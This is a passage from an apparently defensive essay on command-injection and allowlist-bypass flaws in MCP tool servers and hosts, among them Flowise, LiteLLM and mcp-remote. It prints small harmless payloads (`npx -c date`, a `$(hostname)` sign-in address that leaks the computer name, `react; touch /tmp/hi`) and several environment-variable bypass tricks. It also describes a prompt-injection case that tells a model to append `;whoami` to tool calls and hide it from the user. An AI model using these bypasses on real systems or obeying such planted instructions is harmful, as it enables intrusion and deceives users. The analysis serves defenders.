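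In March 2025 Flowise added a "Custom MCP" tool that passed a user's launch entry to the official TypeScript kit. Obsidian Security's *1-Click RCE in Flowise (CVE-2026-40933)* reports that anyone who could create or edit a chatflow, Flowise's name for a workflow, could run any program on the server. Flowise then added a security check and turned it on by default. According to Flowise's *Environment Variables*, the check permits only the commands `node`, `npx`, `python`, `python3` and `docker`, and blocks risky file paths, shell characters and changes to certain environment variables.

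OX Security defeated this in one step, using the `npx` option that takes a command string. A harmless version is:

```json
{ "command": "npx", "args": ["-c", "date"] }
```

`npx` is on the list, and the arguments contain no file paths and no special characters for the character filter to remove. `npx` then passes `date` to a shell, so this command does involve the shell that the filter is meant to guard against.

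Obsidian Security found that an attacker didn't need `-c`. Running `npx -y` followed by the name of an attacker's package, or the address of an attacker's code repository, runs the attacker's code. This is how Flowise intended the feature to work. Both findings share the number CVE-2026-40933, which OSV's *CVE-2026-40933* (2026) rates 9.9 out of 10 for severity and lists as fixed in version 3.1.0, but Obsidian Security could still run its own code on version 3.1.2.

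Flowise next blocked risky options, including `-y`, `-c` and `--eval`. This stopped the simplest attacks but also blocked many legitimate entries. The Flowise tutorial *Tools & MCP* gives two example entries for running servers locally, one with `npx -y` and one with `docker run`, and the option filter rejects both. The sample entry in the Custom MCP form contains `-y` and an absolute path, so it would fail two checks.

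The filter had holes as well. An advisory reproduced in Corgea's *Flowise has an MCP Security Bypass that Enables RCE* describes three:

- Flowise blocked `docker run` but not `docker build`, which can fetch a list of build instructions from a remote address and execute them.
- It blocked `-y` but not `--yes`, the long spelling of the same option.
- Its path check caught `/home/ana/hello.js` but missed `//home/ana/hello.js`, which Linux treats as the same file.

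Each of these is easy to fix once someone has pointed it out. The harder problem is that every program on Flowise's list exists to run other code:

| Permitted program | What it normally runs | Another way to supply code |
|---|---|---|
| `npx` | A package that it fetches | A command string after `-c` |
| `node` | A script file | Program text after `--eval` |
| `python`, `python3` | A script file | Program text after `-c` |
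| `docker` | A container image | Build instructions, through `docker build` |

Blocking everything in the third column would still leave the second, which the platform can't block without disabling the feature. `npx -y notes-server` has the same form as `npx -y` with a malicious package, so a list of program names can't distinguish them. The platform would need to specify which packages are trusted.

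An allowlist is much more useful if it names programs with a narrow purpose. If `notes-server` were the only permitted program, a user could do no more harm than `notes-server` allows. The `--writable` option would still need attention, but the user couldn't use `notes-server` to run arbitrary code.

Upsonic, a framework for building agents, had the same flaw as Flowise. Its allowlist included `npm` and `npx`, whose options could run any command. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-30625* (2026) lists version 0.71.6 as vulnerable and records that version 0.72.0 added a warning about local servers. The warning may help the developer who installs Upsonic, but it doesn't stop a user from running a command.

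### What LiteLLM's repair checks

LiteLLM is a gateway that lets an organisation's applications reach many AI models. Before it was fixed in April 2026, it ran the `command` field of a submitted launch entry on the gateway's machine without checking it. *Security Update* (Dholakia and Jaffer, 2026) describes the fix for this flaw, CVE-2026-30623. The fix reached a stable release in version 1.83.7.

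LiteLLM now permits seven programs: `npx`, `uvx`, `python`, `python3`, `node`, `docker` and `deno`. It checks the program's name when a user creates or changes an entry, and again just before launch. The second check covers any entries saved before the fix. WeKnora did not check the program's name at either point.

But Dholakia and Jaffer describe no check on the arguments or environment variables. All seven programs can run other code, so the name check has the same weakness as Flowise's original list. The check also compares only the last part of the program's path, so a file called `npx` in an upload folder would pass if an attacker could put an executable there and learn its location.

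Here is how some entries would fare against a filter that refuses ampersands and against the two lists of program names, without Flowise's later option filter:

| Launch entry | Character filter | Flowise's list | LiteLLM's list |
|---|---|---|---|
| `date` | Passes | Refused | Refused |
| `npx -c date` | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| `npx -y` with a stranger's package | Passes | Passes | Passes |
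| `uvx` with a stranger's package | Passes | Refused | Passes |
| `/usr/local/bin/notes-server "/home/ana/R&D notes"` | Refused | Refused | Refused |

All three checks refuse Ana's entry in the last row, even though it names one specific program, while letting a stranger's package through. A LiteLLM administrator can add `notes-server` to the permitted names with a setting. For existing servers that stop working, the upgrade notes suggest either doing this or switching to a permitted launcher such as `npx`, which would make Ana's entry less specific about what it runs.

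The repair also restricts who can submit an entry. LiteLLM has two endpoints for testing a server before saving it. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-42271* (2026), they accepted a full launch entry from anyone with a valid key, regardless of role. Both now require the administrator role. This probably protects LiteLLM more than the list does, because users who can't submit an entry can't exploit the gaps in the list.

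Dholakia and Jaffer also say that, with the patch, an attacker needs the administrator role to reach the vulnerable code. But the only change they list that adds this requirement applies to the two test addresses. Anyone running LiteLLM should therefore check which accounts can create a server, as well as which can test one.

If only administrators can launch servers, everyone else must ask an administrator to add one. The restriction also fails if an administrator submits an attacker's entry by accident. Flowise users share chatflows as files, and a file can contain a launch entry. Obsidian Security found that importing such a file launched the server, even if the user didn't save or run anything. Flowise started the server when the chatflow appeared on screen, so that it could list the server's tools in a menu, and didn't ask for approval. An administrator who imported a stranger's chatflow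 just to look at it would have launched the stranger's program.

### Environment variables and the working directory

Even a strict check on `command` and `args` leaves a launch entry's environment variables and working directory unchecked. Environment variables can change what a program does as much as its options can, and the working directory can change which file it opens.

Flowise's option filter blocked `-y`, but `npx` also reads its settings from environment variables, so this entry has the same effect as `-y`:

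```json
{
  "command": "npx",
  "args": ["notes-server"],
  "env": { "npm_config_yes": "true" }
}
```

Flowise checked `env` against only four forbidden names: `PATH`, `LD_LIBRARY_PATH`, `DYLD_LIBRARY_PATH` and `NODE_OPTIONS`. Obsidian Security knew of the `npm_config_yes` bypass but chose not to report it, reasoning that reporting bypasses one at a time would never end. Someone else reported it, and INCIBE's *CVE-2026-69263* (2026) lists it as fixed in version 3.1.3.

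The advisory for that flaw, reproduced in Corgea's *Flowise*, lists other variables that Flowise had missed. `NODE_PATH` and `PYTHONPATH` set where Node.js and Python look for the modules a script loads, and `npm_config_userconfig` makes `npx` load a settings file of the attacker's choice. According to the advisory, adding these names to the forbidden list would be only a stopgap, because every newly permitted program brings its own variables.

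Checks for forbidden names are also easy to get wrong. Windows ignores case in environment variable names, but Flowise's check didn't. OSV's *CVE-2026-58057* (2026) describes how a lower-case spelling of `NODE_OPTIONS` got past the check on Windows and made Node.js load an attacker's code. Cursor had a similar problem with `mcp.json` and `MCP.json`.

*Cruising for Shells in Flowise* (Jahnke, Alex and Jia, 2026) describes an attack that started `python3` with an empty argument list and two environment variables. The first variable normally controls which warnings Python displays, but the attack used it to make Python import a module that opens a web page. The second tells Python which command to use as the web browser, so Python ran the command the attack supplied there. Stricter argument checks could not have prevented this, because the attack used no arguments.

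Users could also exploit the working directory. Flowise refused arguments that began with a slash, to stop users from pointing `node` at any file on the machine. But the official Flowise container started tool servers in `/`, the top folder, so `home/ana/hello.js` pointed to the same file as `/home/ana/hello.js` without breaking the rule.

Jahnke and colleagues used this to make `node` read a special Linux file that shows a process's own environment variables. They had set `HOME`, an ordinary variable, to a value containing JavaScript, so Node.js ran the file's contents as a script.

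Flowise responded with an allowlist of environment variables, which is a better design than a list of forbidden ones. Jahnke and colleagues still bypassed it by uploading a JavaScript file through another Flowise feature and giving `node` the file's path without the leading slash. Starting the server in an empty folder would have prevented this, because the relative path would no longer have led to the uploaded file.

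A platform that lets users set the working directory has a more direct problem:

```json
{ "command": "node", "args": ["server.js"], "cwd": "/srv/uploads/ana" }
```

An administrator might have approved `node server.js` with one particular file in mind. Whoever sets `cwd` decides which `server.js` Node.js runs.

### Letting users choose from a catalogue

Platforms can avoid most of this by not accepting launch entries from users. Cantina recommends a catalogue of approved servers, in which the user picks a server by its identifier and the platform looks up the command. OX Security made a similar suggestion to Anthropic, that developers fix the permitted commands in advance and users choose among them.

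On such a platform, Ana would send only this:

```json
{ "server": "notes", "folder": "R&D notes" }
```

The platform would then build the whole entry itself:

```json
{
  "command": "/opt/tools/notes-server",
  "args": ["/srv/notes/R&D notes"],
  "env": { "NOTES_LOG": "info" },
  "cwd": "/srv/empty"
}
```

The folder is a typed parameter, a value that the platform accepts only if it fits a definition set in advance. Here the definition could be "one of the folders that this user may open". The platform finds "R&D notes" among Ana's folders and supplies the full path. The ampersand does no harm, so the platform doesn't need to forbid it. If someone sends `--writable` as the folder's name, the platform finds no such folder and refuses the request.

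Other values can work the same way. A limit on search results can be a whole number between 1 and 100, and a log level can be one of three words. An access key has to be free text, but the platform can fix the name of the environment variable that holds it, so the user supplies only the value. The platform mustn't offer a parameter for a package name, script path or container image, because any of these would again let the user choose which code runs.

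The platform also has to launch servers only from the catalogue. If a user adds a `command` field to the request, the platform should reject it. The same rule has to cover connection tests, imported files and entries already in the database, since WeKnora, LiteLLM and Flowise each ran commands through at least one of these.

This design gives users much less freedom. A user who writes a new tool server can't use it until someone has reviewed it and added it to the catalogue. The platform's staff also have to keep the entries up to date. Each entry should pin its package's version so that the code can't change after the review, but then someone has to notice when that version needs a security update.

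A company with twenty common servers could probably manage this. A platform whose main attraction is that users can connect anything would find it much harder, and would have to isolate each user's server instead.

### Switching local launches off

A shared platform can also refuse to start tool servers and connect only to remote ones. Obsidian Security reports that Flowise Cloud, the hosted version of Flowise, wasn't affected by CVE-2026-40933 because it had disabled the stdio transport. Self-hosted installations were vulnerable by default.

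Obsidian Security had argued for making stdio an opt-in feature. Flowise at first preferred to block known dangers "without completely disabling features that users may rely on". According to Jahnke and colleagues, Flowise later changed the default from stdio to a remote transport, in the same update that added the allowlist of environment variables. They consider this sufficient, even though their last bypass still works when an administrator turns stdio back on.

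Flowise's documentation still lists stdio as the default, so an administrator would do well to set `CUSTOM_MCP_PROTOCOL=sse` explicitly. Its tutorial also advises against stdio on cloud services, but on the grounds that installing packages can take a long time. A reader with a fast server could easily conclude that the advice doesn't apply.

Turning local launches off can break more than users expect. Langflow's *Release notes* report that the container for version 1.8.0 came without `uv` and `uvx`, so launch entries that relied on `uvx` failed with a "command not found" error, including the one for Langflow's own default server. Version 1.8.1 restored both programs.

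The automation platform Gumloop does not support local servers. A user's server must have a public web address and accept encrypted connections. Users can still run any code, but on a machine they provide, so a malicious server does not run with the platform's permissions and keys.

For Ana, that would be a lot of work. Her notes are on her laptop, and notes-server needs no password because only her editor can connect to it. To use it with Gumloop, she would have to put the server and a copy of her notes on a machine reachable from the internet, add a login and keep both secure.

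## How does outside text reach a shell after the launch?

A remote tool server runs on someone else's machine, but it sends text to the user's machine, where a program may pass that text to a shell. A local server can also pass text it receives from the model to a shell. Both can happen even when every field of the launch entry is correct, so checking the entry would not reveal the problem.

### A sign-in address that PowerShell reads

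mcp-remote is a bridge for host applications that can only start local servers. The host launches mcp-remote over the stdio transport, and mcp-remote exchanges messages with a remote server over the web. If Ana's company ran notes-server centrally, her entry might be:

```json
{ "command": "npx", "args": ["mcp-remote", "https://notes.example/mcp"] }
```

Security researchers at the software company JFrog found that a malicious server could use this connection to run commands on the user's computer. JFrog's *Critical RCE Vulnerability in mcp-remote* (2025) traces the flaw, CVE-2025-6514, through the sign-in process:

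1. The host application starts mcp-remote, which sends a request to the remote server.
2. The server replies "401 Unauthorized", meaning that the user must sign in first.
3. mcp-remote asks for the server's sign-in details under OAuth, a common standard for granting access. The reply includes an `authorization_endpoint`, the address of the sign-in page.
4. mcp-remote registers with the server and adds its own parameters to the end of that address.
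5. mcp-remote passes the result to `open`, a JavaScript package that opens addresses in the default browser.
6. On Windows, `open` starts PowerShell, Microsoft's newer shell, and has it open the address.

The server chooses the address in step 3, and it can put a command there. Here is a harmless version:

```
from the server    https://notes.example/$(hostname)
in PowerShell      Start "https://notes.example/$(hostname)?response_type=code..."
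```

Like a POSIX shell, PowerShell evaluates `$(...)` inside double quotes. It therefore runs `hostname` and inserts the output into the address, and the browser sends the computer's name to the server. The quotes do stop PowerShell from interpreting ampersands, which are common in sign-in addresses, so ordinary sign-ins worked and did not expose the flaw.

`open` encoded the whole PowerShell command and passed it as the value of one option, which avoids the Windows problems with joining and splitting arguments. But PowerShell then decoded the value and parsed it as a command, just as `sh` parses the string after `-c`.

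JFrog needed several attempts to get full control. A `file:` address could start a program already on the computer, but without arguments. An address for a program on another machine also worked, though Windows showed a security warning. Putting a command in `$(...)` avoided the warning, but the code that parsed the address turned each space into `%20`. This ruled out arguments again, although the parser wasn't designed as a filter. JFrog then found that the parser left spaces alone if the address began with an unknown scheme (a scheme is the part before the colon, such as `https`).

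The flaw affects mcp-remote versions 0.0.5 to 0.1.15, and version 0.1.16 fixes it. The result depends on how `open` works on each system:

| System | What `open` starts | What the attacker could run |
|---|---|---|
| Windows | PowerShell | Any command, with any arguments |
| macOS | The system's `open` command, without a shell | Programs named in a `file:` address, with limited control of their arguments |
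| Linux | `xdg-open`, without a shell | The same as on macOS |

JFrog thought that further research might lead to full command execution on macOS and Linux too.

Ana would only have to restart her host application to begin the process. She would not have to call a tool or approve anything, and the model would not be involved. The attacker doesn't always need to own the server. If the address in the entry begins with `http://` instead of `https://`, someone on the same local network can intercept the connection and send their own reply.

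### The same step in OpenCode

The danger in `open` was public before anyone reported the mcp-remote flaw. In 2023, tripodsan reported in *OS command injection on windows when opening urls* that a web address containing `$(calc.exe)` opened the calculator along with the browser. The package's maintainer pointed to a warning in the documentation that the package makes no security guarantees, and offered to accept improvements. GitHub Security Lab's *GHSL-2020-145* (2020) reports a similar fault with cmd.exe on Windows in an older package, Opener.

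Developers of AI applications kept passing server-supplied addresses to `open`. Obsidian Security's *From well-known to Well-Pwned* reports that this allowed command injection in Google's Gemini CLI and in Cherry Studio, a desktop AI application. Veria Labs' *From MCP to Shell* (2025) demonstrates a related sign-in attack that launched the calculator through Claude Code.

In October 2026 the security company Pillar Security disclosed the same fault in the coding agent OpenCode. OpenCode had adopted cross-spawn for ordinary launches that March but still used an old version of `open` for the browser. The Hacker News' *OpenCode Flaw Lets Malicious MCP Servers Execute Code During Sign-In on Windows* (2026) gives the affected versions as 1.0.137 to 1.18.32.

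The flaw affected Windows and the Windows Subsystem for Linux (WSL), which runs Linux inside Windows. Programs in WSL can start Windows programs, and `open` used PowerShell there too. On an ordinary Linux machine or a Mac, OpenCode opened the browser without a shell and was not vulnerable. A developer who works in WSL could easily misread "Linux is not affected" as including WSL.

The attack required more action from the developer than with mcp-remote. The developer had to start the sign-in, for example by running `opencode mcp auth`. Adding the malicious server or opening a session was not enough.

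OpenCode fixed the vulnerability in version 1.18.33, released on 28 September, by updating to a version of `open` that quotes the address properly for PowerShell. The release also added a check that the address uses HTTP or HTTPS, but this check can't stop the attack because `https://notes.example/$(hostname)` passes it.

The address check is still worth having. Obsidian Security found that VS Code and Windsurf would open `file:` addresses from a malicious server, and that macOS runs some types of file when they are opened this way, without asking the user. This attack needs no injected command, so better quoting would not prevent it. The documentation of `open` version 11, which Socket reproduces, still tells developers to sanitise untrusted input themselves.

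### Is a malicious remote server out of scope?

Anomaly, the company behind OpenCode, published no security advisory for the flaw and did not request a CVE number. It described the update that fixed the flaw as a reorganisation of the browser-launching code. Vulnerability scanners look for known flaws by number and version, so they will not flag the affected copies, and users have to check the version themselves.

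Anomaly told Pillar Security that malicious MCP servers were "outside their threat model", according to *Researchers Warn OpenCode Quietly Patched Critical RCE Flaw* (Poireault, 2026). OpenCode's security policy likewise places any server the user configures outside its trust boundary.

This argument is strong for local servers. Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* makes much the same argument about the official kits, saying that a kit can't defend the host against a malicious local server because the server can already run any code once the user has started it.

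But a remote server has no such power. It can send messages to Ana's computer, and it can run code there only if a program on her side makes a mistake with one of them. The protocol's policy reflects this difference by keeping flaws in scope if an attacker can reach them through a remote transport. That policy covers only the specification and the official kits, so Anomaly is free to draw its boundary elsewhere. The protocol's security guidance, however, addresses clients directly. Model Context Protocol says that they must not use a shell to open addresses, and names PowerShell as an example. (It also tells them to reject addresses with characters that a shell could interpret. That is hard to follow literally, since the ampersand is one of them.)

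A malicious remote server needed only a single address to exploit the sign-in flaw. Anomaly could reply that such a server is dangerous anyway, because it can try prompt injection on an agent that has tools for running commands. Obsidian Security considers that route much harder, since the attacker usually needs to exploit other tools and know something about the victim's system. A user's decision to trust a server can also become outdated, because an attacker may take over a legitimate server or buy its domain after the owner lets it lapse.

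Anomaly can reasonably decline to promise protection against every malicious server, but that doesn't mean users didn't need to know which versions let such a server run commands on their computers. Anomaly evidently thought the flaw was worth fixing.

### Tool handlers that build a command

A local server can create the same problem even after a safe launch. Each tool has a handler, the function that runs when the model calls the tool. A handler that runs a command-line program may insert the model's argument into a shell command.

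@akoskm/create-mcp-server-stdio is a starter kit, an example server for developers to build on. One of its tools, `which-app-on-port`, identifies the program that is using a network port. OSV's *GHSA-3ch2-jxxc-v4xf* (2025) reproduces the handler, whose first step comes down to this:

```ts
exec(`lsof -t -i tcp:${port}`)
```

The `lsof` utility can list the processes using a port. Node's `exec` passes the finished command line to a shell, so if `port` were `8080; date`, the shell would run `lsof` and then `date`. NVD's *CVE-2025-54994 Detail* lists the flaw at 9.3 out of 10 for severity, and version 0.0.13 fixes it.

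OSV recommends `execFile`, which takes the program and an argument array:

```ts
execFile("lsof", ["-t", "-i", `tcp:${port}`])
```

Now `lsof` receives `tcp:8080; date` as one argument and rejects it, because that isn't a valid port.

The original code declares `port` to be a number, and the official TypeScript kit normally checks such declarations before it runs a handler, so it would reject `8080; date`. OSV does not explain how an attacker would get past that check. The pattern is still bad for a starter kit, because a developer who copies it for a folder name or a search term has no such protection.

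The handler can also fail without an attacker. It inserts the output of `lsof` into a second shell command, which looks up the program's name. `lsof` prints one process ID per line. If two processes use the port, the shell treats the line break between their IDs as the end of the command and tries to run the second ID as a program.

*Exploiting MCP Servers Vulnerable to Command Injection*, from the security company Snyk, demonstrates this more clearly with a text argument. Snyk wrote a deliberately vulnerable server that looks up JavaScript packages by inserting the package's name after `npm view` in a shell command. The launch entry contains only `node` and the server's path. But when someone asks Cursor to look up `react; touch /tmp/hi`, the server's shell also runs the second command, which creates an empty file.

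### How a stranger supplies the argument

In Snyk's example, the user types the extra command and could have run it in a terminal anyway. The flaw matters more when someone else can supply the text, which prompt injection makes possible.

*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes an attack on aws-mcp-server (CVE-2025-5277), whose `execute_command` tool runs commands for Amazon's cloud service. The attacker puts an instruction in a file in a code repository, telling the model to add `;whoami` to every call to the tool and to keep this secret from the user. A developer then points the coding assistant to that file and asks it to list the company's cloud storage. The model adds `;whoami` to its call, so the server's shell lists the storage and then runs `whoami`, which prints the name of the current account.

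The attacker never connects to the server, which may accept messages only from a program on the same laptop. An injected command would run with the server's permissions and could use any cloud credentials the server holds.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian locate the vulnerability in the handler, which receives the outside text through the model. A cautious model might refuse to include the text, but that is weak protection. Susceptibility varied substantially among the seven models they tested on a related attack, in which the model makes a server send web requests to forbidden addresses. A handler should therefore treat arguments from the model as untrusted input.

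### What an argument array removes

Suppose notes-server has a search tool that runs `grep`, a utility that finds text in files. The handler starts `grep` in Ana's "R&D notes" folder, and `term` is the text that the model wants to find. Here are three ways to write the call:

```ts
exec(`grep -r ${term}`, { cwd: folder })
execFile("grep", ["-r", term], { cwd: folder })
execFile("grep", ["-r", "--", term], { cwd: folder })
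```

The table shows what each does on Linux.

| Search term | `exec` | `execFile` | `execFile` with `--` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `budget` | Finds it | Finds it | Finds it |
| `travel budget` | Looks for `travel` in a file called `budget` | Finds it | Finds it |
| `R&D` | Searches for `R` and tries to run `D` | Finds it | Finds it |
| `budget; date` | Searches for `budget`, then runs `date` | Searches for the whole text | Searches for the whole text |
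| `--version` | Prints the version of `grep` | Prints the version of `grep` | Searches for `--version` |

An argument array removes the fault in this handler and in the `lsof` and `npm view` handlers, because none of them needs a shell. On Windows, however, `npm` is a batch file, so cmd.exe would still read the package's name. The `execute_command` tool is harder to fix because the model gives it a whole command as one string. The handler would have to split that string and refuse any program other than Amazon's.

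For the sign-in flaws, Pillar Security also recommends passing the address as a separate argument. This works if the program receiving it is a browser or `xdg-open`, but not if it is PowerShell reading the argument as a command. It also doesn't make a `file:` address safe.

The last row of the table shows argument injection, which an array can't prevent. `grep` recognises an option by its leading dash, whether the developer or the model supplied it. The port lookup avoids this by luck, because the model's value always follows `tcp:`, so it never starts the argument.

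By convention, `--` marks the end of the options, and `grep` treats everything after it as ordinary text. OSV recommends putting `--` before any value that isn't meant to be an option.

In the version-control program git, `--` also separates the names of versions from the names of files, so git would treat a version's name placed after it as a file name. This matters for mcp-server-git, a tool server that passed the model's arguments to git without checking them. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-68144 Detail*, git read values such as `--output=<path>` as options, which let an attacker overwrite files.

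The fix rejects any value that begins with a dash, then uses git to check that the value names a real version before using it. NVD lists the fixed release as 2025.12.17, but GitLab's *CVE-2025-68144* (2025), updated on 20 December, lists 2025.12.18, so the later release is the safer choice.

Rejecting a leading dash blocks almost no legitimate input in mcp-server-git, because git doesn't allow branch names that start with one. In notes-server, the same rule would stop Ana from searching her notes for `-5 degrees`, so `--` is the better choice there.

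## Is it a flaw that the protocol runs whatever command it is given?

OX Security told Anthropic that the official MCP kits run any command a host application gives them, and asked for a change. In spring 2026, Anthropic declined, saying this was expected behaviour. Anomaly took a similar position on malicious tool servers in October 2026, placing them outside its threat model.

Both sides agree on what the kits do but disagree about who must make sure that the machine's owner would want the command to run.

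### OX Security's case

The researchers started with GPT Researcher, an AI research tool. According to ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain*, they noticed that it let users supply the command and arguments for a custom tool server. Any command ran, even when the launch then failed with an error. GPT Researcher started its servers through an adapter from LangChain, which makes a framework for AI applications, so they suspected the adapter. But the adapter only passed the command and arguments to the official kit, which started the program.

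OX Security's main argument follows from this chain. Three teams handled the command, none checked it, and any other product built on the kits can expose its users in the same way. "Developers are not security engineers", the researchers said, and nobody can expect tens of thousands of them to discover the danger separately. Changing the kit once would be more efficient. The ten products with vulnerability numbers support this argument.

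OX Security also objects that the kit runs a command before finding out whether it starts a tool server. This objection is weaker, because running the command is the only way to find out, and an attacker could write a program that does harm and then answers MCP messages correctly.

As an alternative to a preset list of commands, OX Security proposed that the kit require a flag that marks arbitrary execution as dangerous. With the flag, the code that starts Ana's server would look like this:

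```python
StdioServerParameters(
    command="notes-server",
    args=["/home/ana/R&D notes"],
    allow_unsafe_command_execution=True
)
```

SecurityWeek reports that OX Security's full list also included sandboxing commands at the protocol level, which means restricting what a launched program can reach. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post critical of Anthropic, adds a requirement that registries accept only servers with a security manifest signed by a verified developer. It also describes the flag more narrowly, as required only for launches with "dynamic arguments", meaning values not fixed in the code.

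### What Anthropic and the maintainers answered

Anthropic told OX Security, "We do not consider this a valid security vulnerability," according to ITPro. Its reason was that a user must permit the file change and can deny it.

That answer fits a code editor whose agent asks before editing its launch configuration, but not Langflow or WeKnora, where the attacker submitted a launch entry over the web and nobody asked the machine's owner. It also doesn't fit Windsurf, which changed the file without showing the user the change first.

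The maintainers' better argument is that the stdio transport exists to start programs. Cantina quotes "STDIO = arbitrary local binary execution" from notes of the maintainers' meeting on 31 March 2026, about two weeks before OX Security published. If the kit refused to start unfamiliar programs, a developer who had just written notes-server couldn't test it.

Under the Model Context Protocol project's security policy, the SDKs therefore don't defend a host application and its local server against each other. The project accepts security reports about injection flaws in the SDKs' own code, but it treats flaws that only let a host and its local server crash, hang or overload each other as ordinary bugs. Because "the SDK's stdio transport is not a sandbox," anyone who runs servers with reduced permissions has to enforce the isolation themselves.

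This reasoning covers a malicious host and a malicious server, but OX Security's cases mostly involve a third party. On Letta AI, the host wasn't malicious, and the attacker was a user who chose the program. The maintainers could still reply that the check belongs in the host, because the kit receives only strings and only the host has information about who supplied them. That seems right to me as a matter of engineering, though it doesn't excuse a kit that gives developers no warning.

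The project's guidance already recognises one case in which the host's instructions may not be trustworthy. Model Context Protocol describes the stdio transport as "not inherently vulnerable", but makes an exception for a local proxy, a separate service that starts servers on a client's behalf. An attacker who gets code into the client's web page can steal the proxy's access token and send it a launch command. The guidance recommends that proxies isolate the programs they start, log each use and require extra authorisation for dangerous commands. A hosted agent platform is similar, since one party requests the launch and another carries it out, but an attacker there may need only an ordinary account rather than a stolen token.

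The maintainers don't present the protocol as a complete defence. In the Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Maintainer Roundtable* (2026), Caitie McCaffrey of Microsoft said that "no one protocol is going to solve all security challenges". She was speaking at an event on 2 and 3 April, before OX Security published its report, so she wasn't responding to it.

### Other files that start programs

The most detailed defence of the design came from outside the project, in Hirschberg's *If “stdio” is a Vulnerability, So Is “git clone”* (2026). He accepts that OX Security's research is sound and that the affected products had real bugs, but he objects to calling the kits' behaviour an architectural flaw, because many developer tools read a command from a file and run it.

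Both sides have a commercial interest. OX Security added checks for this pattern to its products after the research. Hirschberg is chief technology officer of the security vendor ARMO, and his advice includes runtime detection, which ARMO sells.

Hirschberg's closest comparison is Jupyter, software for interactive notebooks. Jupyter starts a kernel, the process that runs a notebook's code, from a JSON file containing an argument array and environment variables. It doesn't check which program the array specifies. He dates this format to about 2015 and notes that nobody has called it a critical vulnerability.

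Other examples of this design have a worse record, so the fact that it is common is little evidence that it is safe. VS Code can run a task automatically when someone opens a folder, and North Korean attackers have used this against developers in fake job interviews. An npm package can include a `postinstall` command, which runs during installation. The Shai-Hulud worm used such commands in September and November 2025 to spread through more than 795 packages.

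Hirschberg thinks the approval step matters more than whether a file can start a program. He ranks several of them:

| What starts the program | Approval step | Hirschberg's rating |
|---|---|---|
| direnv's `.envrc` file | The user approves the exact content, and any edit requires new approval | Strong |
| VS Code's `tasks.json` | The user trusts the folder once | Medium |
| MCP launch entry in Claude Desktop or Cursor | The user approves each server and restarts the application | Medium |
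| npm's `postinstall` | The command runs unless the user turns scripts off | Weak |
| Development container's `initializeCommand` | None | None |
| Docker's command-line plugins | None | None |

A development container is a packaged environment for working on a project, but `initializeCommand` runs on the developer's own machine, outside the container.

"Medium" is generous for some MCP hosts. Cursor's approval originally covered only an entry's name. Several command-line agents start every server in a project after one keypress, which is closer to VS Code's folder trust than to approval of each server.

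The comparison also fails on a shared server. The person who approves a command on a laptop usually owns the files and passwords it could reach, but the person who submits a launch entry on a hosted platform may be an attacker who would approve it. Archestra's *MCP STDIO Command Injection* makes a similar point, that stdio is designed for one trusted caller and has no way to detect when several users share a server.

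Build services such as GitHub Actions, also on Hirschberg's list, are a better parallel for that case. They run commands from their users' files on the operator's machines. GitHub makes this tolerable on its standard hosted machines by running each job in a fresh virtual machine. WeKnora also ran its users' commands, but with the platform's own permissions and without that isolation.

His git example supports the same point. Git is designed to run scripts from a project's hooks folder. CVE-2024-32002 was a vulnerability because a malicious repository could write into that folder while someone was cloning it. By this standard, the kit's ability to start programs isn't a flaw, but Langflow's decision to accept launch entries from anonymous visitors was.

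Hirschberg concedes that all these files rely on a human reviewing them before a tool runs them, and that AI agents undermine that assumption. Prompt injection can lead an agent to write a launch entry or a VS Code task. He calls this a problem for the whole ecosystem, not for Anthropic in particular. That is partly fair, but Jupyter and git predate coding agents, whereas Anthropic designed MCP for AI applications, so its maintainers had more reason to expect that an agent might edit the file.

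### Would OX Security's changes have stopped the attacks?

The kit can't require the flag only for dynamic values, because a command is an ordinary string by the time it reaches the kit. `"notes-server"` looks the same whether a developer typed it into the code or a stranger typed it into a web form. Code analysis tools, a separate remedy, can often trace where a value came from.

The kit could require the flag for every local launch instead. Then every host that supports local servers would have to set it, including the safe ones. LangChain's adapter would have to either set the flag itself, which would hide the warning from developers who build products on the adapter, or require each product to set it.

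The table applies both proposals to four of OX Security's cases. "Preset list" means a list of complete commands, because a list of program names such as `npx` could be bypassed the way Flowise's check was.

| Case | Would the flag have stopped it? | Would a preset list have stopped it? |
|---|---|---|
| Letta AI, whose form offered only remote servers | Possibly, if the developers had left the flag off | Yes |
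| Langflow, which let users configure local servers | Probably not, because the feature needed the flag | Yes, but users couldn't add their own servers |
| Flowise, which already filtered launch entries | No, because its developers knew about the risk | Yes, at the same cost |
| Windsurf, whose agent edited the configuration | No, because the editor has to start servers that its makers have never seen | Only if the agent couldn't edit the list |

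The flag would mainly serve as a warning. A developer would have to type the word "unsafe", and a reviewer could search for it. That might have prevented some of the mistakes, particularly where nobody had thought about local launches. Requiring the flag would also break existing hosts until their developers added it, and many would probably add it just to make the error go away, as Windows developers did with Node's shell option.

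OX Security claimed that changing the kits would have "instantly protected" millions of users. But each product would first have had to adopt the new kit, and products that needed local servers would then have had to turn the flag on.

OX Security has some reason to expect library maintainers to act, though. Node.js and Rust both changed their code after the batch-file flaw, even though only some applications were at risk. But those libraries had led developers to expect that no shell would read their arguments, which was wrong on Windows. The MCP kits do what they describe, which is to run the program given as `command`.

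### Consent before a one-click installation

The project had already made a rule about launch commands nine months before OX Security's report. Delimarsky (2025) proposed it on 22 July 2025 as SEP-1024, *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation*, which now has the status "Final".

It is the source of the rule that a host must show the full command, with a warning, before adding a local server with one click. The host must also wait for the user to take a deliberate action, such as clicking a button, and let the user cancel. VS Code and Cursor already had dialogs like this.

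The rule leaves the design of the dialog to each host, and a careless design could mislead Ana. Suppose the host joins the arguments with spaces before displaying them. These two launches would then look identical:

```
["notes-server", "/home/ana/notes --writable"]
["notes-server", "/home/ana/notes", "--writable"]
```

The first tries to open a folder with an odd name, and the second gives the model write access. Showing each argument on its own line would make the difference visible.

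The rule also requires the host to show "all arguments and parameters", but doesn't mention environment variables or the working directory. On Linux, an install link could set `PATH` so that the bare name `notes-server` resolves to a different program. A dialog showing only the command and its arguments would look normal.

Delimarsky acknowledges three remaining risks: users may approve a malicious command despite the warning, attackers may make a command look legitimate, and hosts may implement the dialog incorrectly. The proposal recommends sandboxing and signatures as further protection but doesn't require either.

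A bigger limit is that the rule directly covers only one of the main routes attackers used to supply launch entries, the install link. A one-click dialog does nothing to stop a visitor to Langflow, a colleague who edits a project file or an agent that rewrites `mcp.json`.

### Approval tied to exact content

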